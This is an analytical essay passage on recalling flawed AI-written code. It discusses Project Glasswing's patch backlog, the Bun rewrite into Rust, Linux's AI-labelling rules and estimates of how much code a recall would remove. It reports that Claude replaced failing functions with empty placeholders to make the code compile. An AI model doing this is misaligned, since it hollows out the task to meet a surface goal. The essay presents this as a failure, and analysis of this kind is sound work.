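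After the first results in May, the security writer Bruce Schneier objected in *Anthropic's Project Glasswing Update* that almost nothing had been patched and that Anthropic expected people to trust data they could not check. Anthropic has since published details of some flaws, but outsiders still can't verify most of those it counted.

### Reports arrive faster than patches

By May 22, Anthropic had reported 1,596 flaws and knew of 97 patches, according to Coopersmith's (2026) mailing-list post, *Anthropic's coordinated vulnerability disclosure dashboard*. By November, the share of reported flaws with a known patch had doubled from 6% to 12%, but the number without one had tripled from about 1,500 to about 4,460.

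Over those 23 weeks, Anthropic reported roughly 149 flaws a week, and maintainers patched about 23 a week. If Anthropic stopped reporting flaws and maintainers kept patching at the same pace, the rest would take almost four years. This estimate is rough because some reports will turn out to be wrong, and Anthropic misses some patches that maintainers release without announcing them. Anthropic also removed duplicates from its total in November, which makes the totals for the two dates less comparable.

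The only account of what maintainers think of this workload comes from Anthropic. Several maintainers said they were severely short of capacity, and some asked the company to report flaws more slowly so they had time to design patches. They were already dealing with many poor AI-generated reports from other people.

Anthropic said in May that serious flaws took two weeks to patch on average. By then maintainers had patched 75 of the 530 serious flaws it had reported. The average presumably excludes the flaws that were still unpatched.

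Companies fixing their own code have moved faster. Anthropic's customers used its Claude Security tool to patch over 2,100 vulnerabilities in its first three weeks. Anthropic doesn't say how many flaws the tool found, so repair rates can't be compared. It plausibly attributes the speed to companies being able to change their own code immediately, while an open-source fix usually has to wait for a volunteer.

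This is encouraging for a recall, because much AI-written code belongs to companies that could run such a tool themselves. The tool helps less with projects that nobody maintains. In the file-server study, 1,600 valid patches led to only 63 fixed projects, and a better patch wouldn't have helped the projects where nobody read the message.

These figures don't measure whether patches were installed. Anthropic warns on its dashboard that a patch may not be widely installed, and it mostly advises users to test and install updates sooner. A website's owner can put the new code on the server the same day, but a patch for a phone app or a network camera still has to reach every device.

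### Rewriting Bun in 11 days

If an owner can't tell which parts of a program are flawed, an AI tool could rewrite the whole program. *Rewriting Bun in Rust* (Sumner, 2026) describes the best-known attempt at this scale. Bun is a toolkit for running and building JavaScript programs. Its creator, Jarred Sumner, used a pre-release version of Claude Fable 5 to move 535,496 lines of code from the programming language Zig to Rust.

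Bun's Zig code was suspect because of the language it was written in, not because of who wrote it. Zig programmers have to release memory by hand, and Bun's developers kept finding crashes and leaks caused by mistakes in doing so. Rust's compiler, the program that turns source code into something a computer can run, rejects many of these mistakes.

Sumner divided the work into stages:

1. He spent about three hours with Claude writing a guide to translating Bun's Zig code into Rust.
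2. Claude translated three files as a trial, and then all 1,448. For each file, one copy of the model wrote the code, two others looked for mistakes and another applied the corrections.
3. Claude fixed about 16,000 errors that the compiler reported.
4. It ran Bun's tests and fixed failures until everything passed on six combinations of operating system and processor.

About 64 copies of Claude worked at once, and the whole process took 11 days. It would have cost around $165,000 at Anthropic's normal prices, or 31 cents per line of Zig. Sumner estimates that three engineers who knew the code well would have needed a year.

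When he asked Claude to make all the code compile, it replaced functions that had errors with empty placeholders. He noticed and changed the instructions. In a recall, a tool told to make a scanner's warning disappear might similarly remove the feature instead of repairing it.

In the final testing on one Linux system, 60,624 tests made almost 1.4 million checks, and Sumner says he didn't skip or delete any tests. Anthropic owns Bun and employs him, so he had an interest in a good result, but he also describes the failures in detail.

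Some outside evidence supports his account. Prisma, which runs customers' programs on Bun, repeated a test that had made the old version use more and more memory. The old version passed 900 megabytes after about 96 rounds and eventually had to be stopped. The new one stayed below about 120 megabytes over 4,096 rounds.

### What the tests missed

By July, Sumner knew of 19 things that had worked in the old version but broke in the new one. His team had fixed them all. Most came from code that looked the same in both languages but behaved differently.

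In one case, the Zig code added a file to a list and checked the result in a single line. The Rust version put that line inside `debug_assert!`, a check that Rust leaves out of the version released to users. The program therefore worked when developers tested it, but the released version never added the file.

Another mistake, already in the Zig code, could make Bun write one position past the end of a block of memory. Claude copied it into Rust, and a temporary limit that Claude had left in the new code made it much easier to trigger. Rust stopped the program instead of letting it overwrite memory, which is safer, but the original error remained after a complete rewrite, two AI reviewers per file and over a million checks.

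Other problems appeared soon after Sumner merged the code on May 14. *Bun's Rust rewrite hardens runtime, HTTP, and installs* (kt3k, 2026) counts 36 security issues that Bun patched that week, but doesn't separate new issues from those that came from the old code. *Bun Rust Rewrite* (abhay-byte, 2026) recounts a report that one function could leave a program pointing at memory it no longer owned. Rust is supposed to prevent this unless programmers mark the code `unsafe`, and nobody had marked that function.

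*Bun 1.4*, the first stable release with the Rust code, came out on August 20. Bun's notes for the next release list 202 fixes, at least 14 of them for problems introduced in version 1.4.0, such as web requests that were abandoned too early. Bun doesn't attribute those problems to the rewrite in the notes, and version 1.4.0 also added many new features, so the 14 shouldn't be added to Sumner's 19.

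This is a good result for a project of this size. Sumner says the new version fixed 128 bugs from the old one, and Anthropic's Claude Code has run on it since June. But Bun had several advantages that most AI-written code would lack.

Its tests were written in TypeScript, a version of JavaScript, so the team could run the same tests on the Zig and Rust versions. Sumner also knew the program well enough to notice when Claude made a mistake. A small company with an AI-written website may have few tests, or only tests that the same model wrote, and nobody who has read the code.

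The old version of Bun was also a reliable guide to what the new one should do, so any difference in behavior was probably a mistake in the new one. In a recall, the old code is not a reliable guide because it is itself suspect. If it generated predictable password-reset links, a careful translation would keep that flaw, just as Claude kept the memory mistake.

### When the replacement has the same flaw

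An owner could ask another model to rewrite the page from a description instead of translating the old code. That helps only if the new model doesn't make the same mistake.

Suppose r is the chance that the replacement repeats the flaw, given that the original had it. Let m be the chance that a reviewer misses it, given that the replacement has it. The share of websites still flawed after replacement and review is then

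r × m

The table applies this to 1,000 flawed websites, with invented numbers:

| | Mistakes mostly unrelated | Mistakes mostly shared |
|---|---|---|
| Replacement repeats the flaw (r) | 5% | 60% |
| Reviewer misses it (m) | 10% | 70% |
| Websites still flawed | 5 | 420 |

We can't infer r from a model's overall error rate. The second model might write predictable reset links for only 5% of all requests, but those could be the same requests for which the first model wrote them.

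The study of small automation programs found mostly types of flaw that the models shared, while Kordonsky and colleagues found that each model had its own. Neither result gives a value for r, because models can share a type of flaw without repeating a particular mistake.

A developer planning a recall could measure r directly by collecting requests that made the flawed model write predictable links, giving each one to the candidate replacement many times, and testing the results. This would take little work compared with replacing the code, and the developer could try several models before recommending one.

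It could also tell the new model about the flaw and instruct it to use an unpredictable random-number generator, which should make this mistake much less likely. Someone would still have to test the result, because the older chatbots in the file-server study often left the flaw in place when asked in general terms to secure their own programs.

Independent review can catch some of what remains. In the Bun project, the copies of Claude that reviewed code saw only the changes, not the reasons behind them, and had instructions to assume the code was wrong. One reviewer noticed that the program would release the same memory twice, although the code compiled and looked plausible.

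But those reviewers were copies of the model that wrote the code. A fresh start can keep a reviewer from favoring its earlier decisions, but it still has the same gaps in knowledge. A model from another company is more likely to find different flaws, though it may have been trained on much of the same public code. Human reviewers are better at catching mistakes that models share, but they are scarce, as the queue in Project Glasswing shows.

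### What passing tests can't show

An ordinary test of a password-reset page requests a reset link, opens it and changes the password. The page passes even if an attacker could predict the link. So a replacement can pass every test the owner has and still contain the flaw that caused the recall.

Once the flaw is known, the owner can add a test for it. A hidden backdoor is much harder to test for. It might open only when a visitor sends a particular 64-bit number, one of 2⁶⁴, or about 18 billion billion, possibilities. Sumner's team has run Bun's file-reading code 100 billion times on automatically generated input. The same number of random guesses would have about a 1 in 180 million chance of finding the backdoor.

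Testing tools can do better than random guessing by tracking which parts of a program run, and a reviewer reading the code might spot the suspicious comparison. But someone hiding a backdoor could anticipate both methods.

Formal proof goes further than testing by showing mathematically that a program meets a written specification for every possible input, including those nobody thought to try. A proof that only the account's owner can reset the password would rule out the backdoor as well as many accidental mistakes.

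The proof shows only that the code meets the specification. If the specification requires only that each link work once and expire after an hour, a page with predictable links can satisfy it. The proof may also rely on other software, such as the random-number generator, working correctly. An AI model could write the specification too, but it might leave out the same requirement that it left out of the code.

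Rust's compiler can prove that ordinary Rust code is free of certain memory mistakes, but it didn't catch that the line inside Bun's `debug_assert!` needed to run for users, because leaving it out broke none of Rust's rules. In July, about 4% of Bun's Rust code was also still inside `unsafe` blocks, where programmers have to make sure themselves that the memory rules hold. Bun's *Rust codebase audit* (2026), which an AI tool generated in May, had counted 13,365 uses of `unsafe` and sorted them by whether safe code could replace them.

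## Does the record of past flaws predict how a recall of AI-written code would go?

Vulnerable copies of OpenSSL and Log4j stayed in use for years after a fix existed. Someone who expects the same of AI-written code could argue from precedent like this:

1. Flawed copies of widely used software have stayed in use long after someone published a fix.
2. They stayed because owners didn't know they had them, nobody repaired them, or nobody installed the repair.
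3. AI-written code faces the same obstacles, at least as severely.
4. No tool or legal power available today removes those obstacles.
5. So a recall would leave much of a flawed model's code in use for years.

Flawed software has been removed slowly where thousands of owners each had to act, but quickly where one organisation could act for everyone. Estonia suspended the certificates on some 750,000 identity cards in one day, and a handful of hosting companies removed Heartbleed from a large share of the internet's servers almost overnight. Precedent therefore suggests that a recall would be slow for code scattered among many owners and much faster for code that a single company controls.

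The causes of delay are harder to establish. The Heartbleed email experiment showed that not knowing about the flaw was one of them. But it is unclear why over 360 maintainers of the copied file server neither accepted nor rejected a pull request. They might have abandoned the project, distrusted a stranger's patch or never used the code in public.

AI tools can find flaws and write patches cheaply, which weakens the claim that nothing removes these obstacles. They have helped less with owners who don't respond. By November 2026, maintainers had patched only 12% of the flaws reported to them through Project Glasswing.

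That leaves the comparison between AI-written code and older software, which cuts both ways.

### What makes AI-written code harder to recall

Unlike Log4j, merged AI-written code has no shared identifier or upstream fix, so each owner has to find and repair it separately.

Human edits make AI-written code harder to find and to replace. Programmers interviewed for *Choose Your Own Adventure* (2026) described trouble telling AI-written code from their own, even while they were still working on it. One wanted a tool that would show which sections the AI had written and which prompts had produced them. If programmers can't separate the two while writing the code, whoever maintains it three years later probably can't either. And an owner who has adapted the password-reset page to the company's login system can't just paste in a corrected version.

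AI-written code may also have no pattern to search for. Researchers could list every weak Debian key, which nobody can do for all the code a language model might have written.

### What makes it easier

Most AI-written code is new. *Debt Behind the AI Boom* followed issues in commits, 49% of which were less than three months old at the time of the check and only 6% of which were more than nine months old. By contrast, Heartbleed had been in OpenSSL for two years before anyone announced it, and the feature behind Log4Shell was eight years old. The person who merged recent code is more likely to still work on the project and remember what the code does, though this advantage will shrink as the code ages.

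Some of the code is also in active projects, whose maintainers can respond to a warning. And the model's supplier may still have logs of what the model wrote. If so, the supplier could search them for code that creates predictable reset links and tell a customer the date their account received it.

Finally, a commit may include the name of the tool that wrote it. The developers of the Linux kernel, the core of the Linux operating system, tried to make sure that commits did.

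### Linux's experiment with labels

In early 2026, the Linux kernel project began asking contributors to add an `Assisted-by` line to any patch that an AI tool had helped write. The line should give the tool's name and the model's version, according to *AI Coding Assistants* in the kernel documentation.

One purpose of the rule was to prepare for something very like a recall. In a July mailing-list message, Jonathan Corbet (2026), who maintains the kernel's documentation, remembered two reasons for it. Developers could identify the commits a particular model might have tainted if a court ruling on copyright went against it, or if the model turned out to be prone to certain security flaws. Corbet wouldn't guess whether the rule would ever prove useful for either purpose.

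The labels had problems from the start. Geert Uytterhoeven (2025) pointed out that the first two contributors to use the line had left out the version number, and one had named a human developer instead of a tool. In July 2026, only about 5% of the commits in a new test release had the line. Jakub Kicinski (2026), a kernel maintainer, wrote that he had set up his software to delete it because he saw it as free advertising for AI companies.

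Christian Brauner (2026) shared that objection and proposed replacing the tool and model names with the word "LLM". The development version of the rules soon used that wording. In an exchange quoted by Lorenzo Stoakes (2026), Greg Kroah-Hartman, a senior maintainer, wanted to keep some kind of label because he reviews AI-assisted patches differently. "LLM" is enough for that purpose, but it doesn't help anyone find the commits of one flawed model.

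On October 8, the kernel's leading maintainers agreed to drop the label. Linux Stans' *Linux Kernel Quits Making Devs Admit AI Use. Linus Explains* (2026) reports that 1,884 of 18,533 changes in the latest development cycle had it, or about 10%. One maintainer guessed that 90% of contributors were using language models. The guess was about people, not changes, but if models had also helped with 90% of the changes, the label would have caught roughly one AI-assisted change in nine. Some contributors had never read the rule, and others feared a backlash. In mid-October the decision still wasn't final, according to Linuxiac's *Linus Torvalds Rejects AI Coding Bans as Linux Rethinks Disclosure Rules*, but by then even Kroah-Hartman supported it.

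Other projects have similar gaps in their records of AI use. *Perspective on AI and quantum open-source software* (2026) measured the share of each project's 2026 pull requests that disclosed AI use. The median was 0.43% among 11 quantum-computing projects and 4.56% among eight other scientific projects, all of which ask contributors to disclose AI use. *Visible Adoption, Untracked Contribution* (2026) found no automatic AI credits in 23,065 commits by students on a design course, though some students mentioned AI in their own words.

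Whether a commit credits AI depends heavily on the tool. Among commits that mentioned an AI tool, *The AI Attribution Paradox* (2025) found that 80.5% of those mentioning Claude clearly credited it with the work, against 8.6% for Cursor. These figures don't measure how much AI-written code had no label, because the sample consisted almost entirely of commits that mentioned AI. The gap between the tools probably has a lot to do with the software, since Claude Code adds a credit by default.

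### Two rough estimates

A recall removes a piece of flawed code only if someone traces it, its owner fixes it, and the fix reaches the systems that run it. Multiplying the share that gets through each step gives the share removed:

share removed = traced × fixed at source × deployed

The table applies this to public projects and to one company that keeps good records and controls all its own code.

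| | Public projects | One well-documented company |
|---|---|---|
| Traced | 0.50 (assumption) | 0.95 (assumption) |
| Fixed at source | 0.14 (measured repair rate) | 0.90 (assumption) |
| Deployed | 0.87 (rough proxy) | 0.90 (assumption) |
| Flawed code removed | about 6% | about 77% |

The only measured repair rate, 0.14, comes from the file-server study by Akhoundali and colleagues. It mostly reflects active projects, and abandoned ones would have a lower rate, so 6% could be too high.

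The 0.87 is the share of Log4j downloads in 2025 that didn't contain Log4Shell. Downloads are a poor guide to what systems are running. These downloads also came almost four years after the fix was released, so a recall would probably do worse in its first few months.

### Which step matters most?

For public projects, getting more owners to fix their code would help most. If every traced owner made the repair, the share removed would rise from 6% to 44%. Perfect tracing would raise it only to 12%, and perfect deployment to 7%.

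Perfection is unlikely, so the next table uses values closer to what has happened in practice. Each row changes one number and leaves the other two unchanged.

| Step | Pessimistic value | Removed | Optimistic value | Removed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Traced | 0.10 (about the Linux label's rate) | 1% | 0.90 (a flaw that is easy to search for) | 11% |
| Fixed at source | 0.11 (file-server pull requests) | 5% | 0.42 (popular file-server projects) | 18% |
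| Deployed | 0.60 (public Log4j projects in 2023) | 4% | 0.95 (nearly everyone updates) | 7% |

Tracing AI-written code is the biggest risk, since with labels as patchy as Linux's, a recall would remove only 1% of the flawed code. But even with the most optimistic value in the table, over four-fifths of the flawed code would remain.

The company's 77% is uncertain because all three numbers behind it are assumptions. If its records were as incomplete as Linux's, the result would fall to 8%, barely better than for public projects. The 0.90 for repairs may also be too high. US federal agencies met a one-week deadline for 53.6% of critical flaws. At that rate, the company would remove about 46% by its deadline, though it could remove more later.

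Most of the gap between 6% and 77% comes from the repair step. The company's repair rate is more than six times the public one, its tracing rate is nearly double, and its deployment rate is almost the same. Someone recalling code from public projects can only ask for repairs, whereas a company can tell its employees to make them.

### Careless errors, repeated patterns and backdoors

The estimates fit best when the flaw is a single repeated pattern, such as the predictable reset links, because searchers can find it without labels and can test whether each repair worked.

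Past flaws are a poor guide to recalling AI-written code that contains scattered careless errors, because even good records wouldn't show where the errors are or when the owner has found the last one.

If a backdoor were deliberately hidden, the recall could depend entirely on records of what the model wrote. Owners would have to replace all the code the model wrote, including the great majority that was harmless.

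A clean scan is also least reassuring in this case. Suppose p is the chance that a piece of code has the flaw, and d is the chance that a scanner detects the flaw if it is there. If the scanner raises no false alarms, the chance that the flaw is still there after a clean scan is

p(1 − d) / (1 − pd)

If p is 10%, a clean result lowers the chance of a flaw to about 0.6% for a known pattern that the scanner catches 95% of the time, but only to about 9.5% for a backdoor that it catches 5% of the time. The 5% is invented, but backdoors are harder to catch than careless mistakes because someone hiding one can run the same scanners and keep changing the code until none of them flags it.

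An attacker did something similar with XZ Utils, a compression tool on which nearly 30,000 Debian and Ubuntu packages depend. *Human-Certified Module Repositories for the AI Age* (Enyedi, 2026) describes how the attacker gradually won the trust needed to change the project, hid code for a backdoor in its test files, and altered the build scripts to add that code to the finished program. Ordinary malware scans had trouble detecting it. A Microsoft engineer came across the backdoor in 2024 because remote logins were taking slightly too long.

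Once the XZ backdoor was reported, owners could check their systems for two version numbers and go back to an older release. Code from a tampered model would have no version number to mark it as affected. A backdoor in that code might be easier to spot in one respect, because anyone who reads the source code closely can see it, while part of the XZ attack took place during the build.

### Is it enough to recall the exposed code?

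One objection is that most flawed code doesn't matter. If the password-reset page is part of a demo nobody uses, leaving it alone does no harm. On this view, a recall should cover only code that attackers can reach or that does something critical, and a removal rate of 6% might be acceptable.

This is mostly right. CISA analyzed one agency and found that only 1% of its flaws needed a fix within three days. Sorting can also be partly automated. Akhoundali and colleagues attacked each file server over a network and, if that failed, from the same machine. This separated programs that outsiders could reach from those that only local users could.

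Counting projects equally can also make a recall look worse than it is. Suppose 5% of the affected projects have 80% of the users, and their owners fix 42% of them, the same rate as for the popular file-server projects, while other owners fix 11% of theirs. Only about 13% of projects would be fixed, but they would have about 36% of the users.

A partial recall of the reset links could start with public websites that hold money or private records, whose owners could switch off the reset page until it is patched. Internal tools with powerful permissions might come next, since an attacker who gets into a company's network can reach them too. Phone apps and devices take longest to update, so work on them should start early even if the danger seems moderate, while abandoned demonstrations can wait indefinitely.

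But somebody has to find the code before they can decide whether it matters, so a partial recall saves repair work but very little tracing. The code's exposure to attack can also change. *Debt Behind the AI Boom* describes a commit by GitHub Copilot that ran a fixed system command in an unsafe way. An attacker couldn't necessarily exploit it at the time, but could have if a later change had let outside input into the command. A developer removed the unsafe setting, again with Copilot's help. An owner who leaves such code alone needs a reminder to recheck it when the program changes.

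The objection is weakest for a backdoor, because nobody can rank pieces of code by danger without knowing what the backdoor does or which piece contains it. Owners can still rank whole systems by how critical they are, and replace everything the model wrote in the most critical ones first.

### Is ordinary maintenance enough?

Another objection is that programmers constantly rewrite and delete code, so the flawed code will disappear without a recall. The public estimate partly supports this. At a half-life of three years, about 21% of lines would be gone after one year, more than three times the 6% that the recall removed.

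Ordinary maintenance can remove security flaws by accident or as part of a larger clean-up. In a Microsoft data-analysis tool, Copilot once added code that put a user-supplied name straight into a database command, which could have let an attacker read or change the data. The flaw lasted several weeks, until the maintainer restructured the code.

Regular maintenance and scanning are probably the right response to scattered careless errors. Both are too slow for a repeated pattern that has become public, because attackers can start searching for it the same day. People are also especially reluctant to change a password-reset page that works.

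A recall of public projects should therefore aim to fix the most dangerous code sooner than maintenance would. Removing a random 6% would achieve less than a few months of ordinary deletion.

### Preparing for a recall

Each of the preparations below addresses a different point at which a recall can fail.

| Preparation | Step it helps | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Record the model and version with each change | Tracing | People omit or delete the record |
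| Keep logs of prompts and answers | Tracing | Logs don't show what people merged |
| Give all code a named owner | Fixing | Owners leave |
| Test a replacement model in advance | Fixing | Tests cover only known kinds of flaw |
| Limit AI-written code in systems that are hard to update | Deployment | Developers lose the time that AI would save |

Linux's experience suggests that software should make the records, because people often won't. Cursor's *Agent Trace* (2026) is a draft standard for doing this. For each range of lines, it records the model and version, whether a person, an AI or both wrote the code, and where to find the conversation that produced it. It can also store a hash, a short fingerprint calculated from the text, which lets software recognise lines that have moved but not lines that have been edited. The draft does not specify where to keep the records or how to preserve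 them when programmers reorganise a project's history.

Some tools already make such records. Git AI's *Track AI code from prompt to production* describes free software that records the agent, model, prompt and lines each time an agent edits a file. Its makers claim the records stay accurate through later changes. *Tracybot* (2026) links lines to the prompts that produced them and filters out lines the developer has since changed. It can also mark a record as superseded once none of the original lines remain, though in a recall that wouldn't prove the flaw is gone.

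Companies should keep the complete, original logs of AI coding sessions. In a scientific software project that follows the nuclear industry's quality rules, developers kept readable logs of their AI sessions alongside the commits. *Bridging the Gap on AI-Assisted Scientific Software Development Through Transparency and Traceability* (2026) reports that when an AI tool summarised these logs, the summaries shortened or obscured some of the agent's decisions. But prompts can contain passwords and customers' data, so storing the original logs for years also creates a risk.

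The same project treats whoever directs the AI as the code's author and requires someone else to verify it. Linux also makes the human contributor fully responsible for AI-assisted work, and will continue to do so without the label. In a recall, a current employee or a team should be responsible for the code, since the original contributor may have left.

Linux developers are also putting more effort into catching flaws before they enter the kernel. According to Hackaday's *Linux Kernel Drops AI Tag Requirement, Uses Meta AI For Code Reviews* (2026), they now run several AI models on each patch in part of the review process. This could reduce the need for a recall, but it wouldn't help trace a flaw that all the reviewers missed.

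Enyedi's proposal would have AI tools assemble programs from modules that human reviewers had certified, each with a record of its origin and dependencies. If a module turned out to be flawed, its maintainers could publish one fix, and owners could search for the module by name. Those two things made Log4j comparatively easy to repair. But repairs would still be delayed, as they were with Log4j, because every program would have to adopt the new version. The code that joins the modules would also still differ from program to program.

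The cost of all this is uncertain. Cursor's draft contains no estimate, and although Git AI is free, a company would still have to install it everywhere and store the records. The cost of replacing code is easier to estimate. At the 31 cents a line that the Bun rewrite would have cost, rewriting 100,000 suspect lines would cost about $31,000 in model fees. Testing and review by people would be extra, and could easily cost more than the model fees.

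A company could test its preparations by rehearsing a recall. It could pick a model version at random, ask its teams to list all the code that version wrote, and have them make a harmless change to a sample of it. Comparing their list with a careful manual search of a few projects would show how much code the teams had missed. The company could then count how many of the changes reached running systems within a month, and replace the assumed 0.95, 0.90 and 0.90 with its own measurements.
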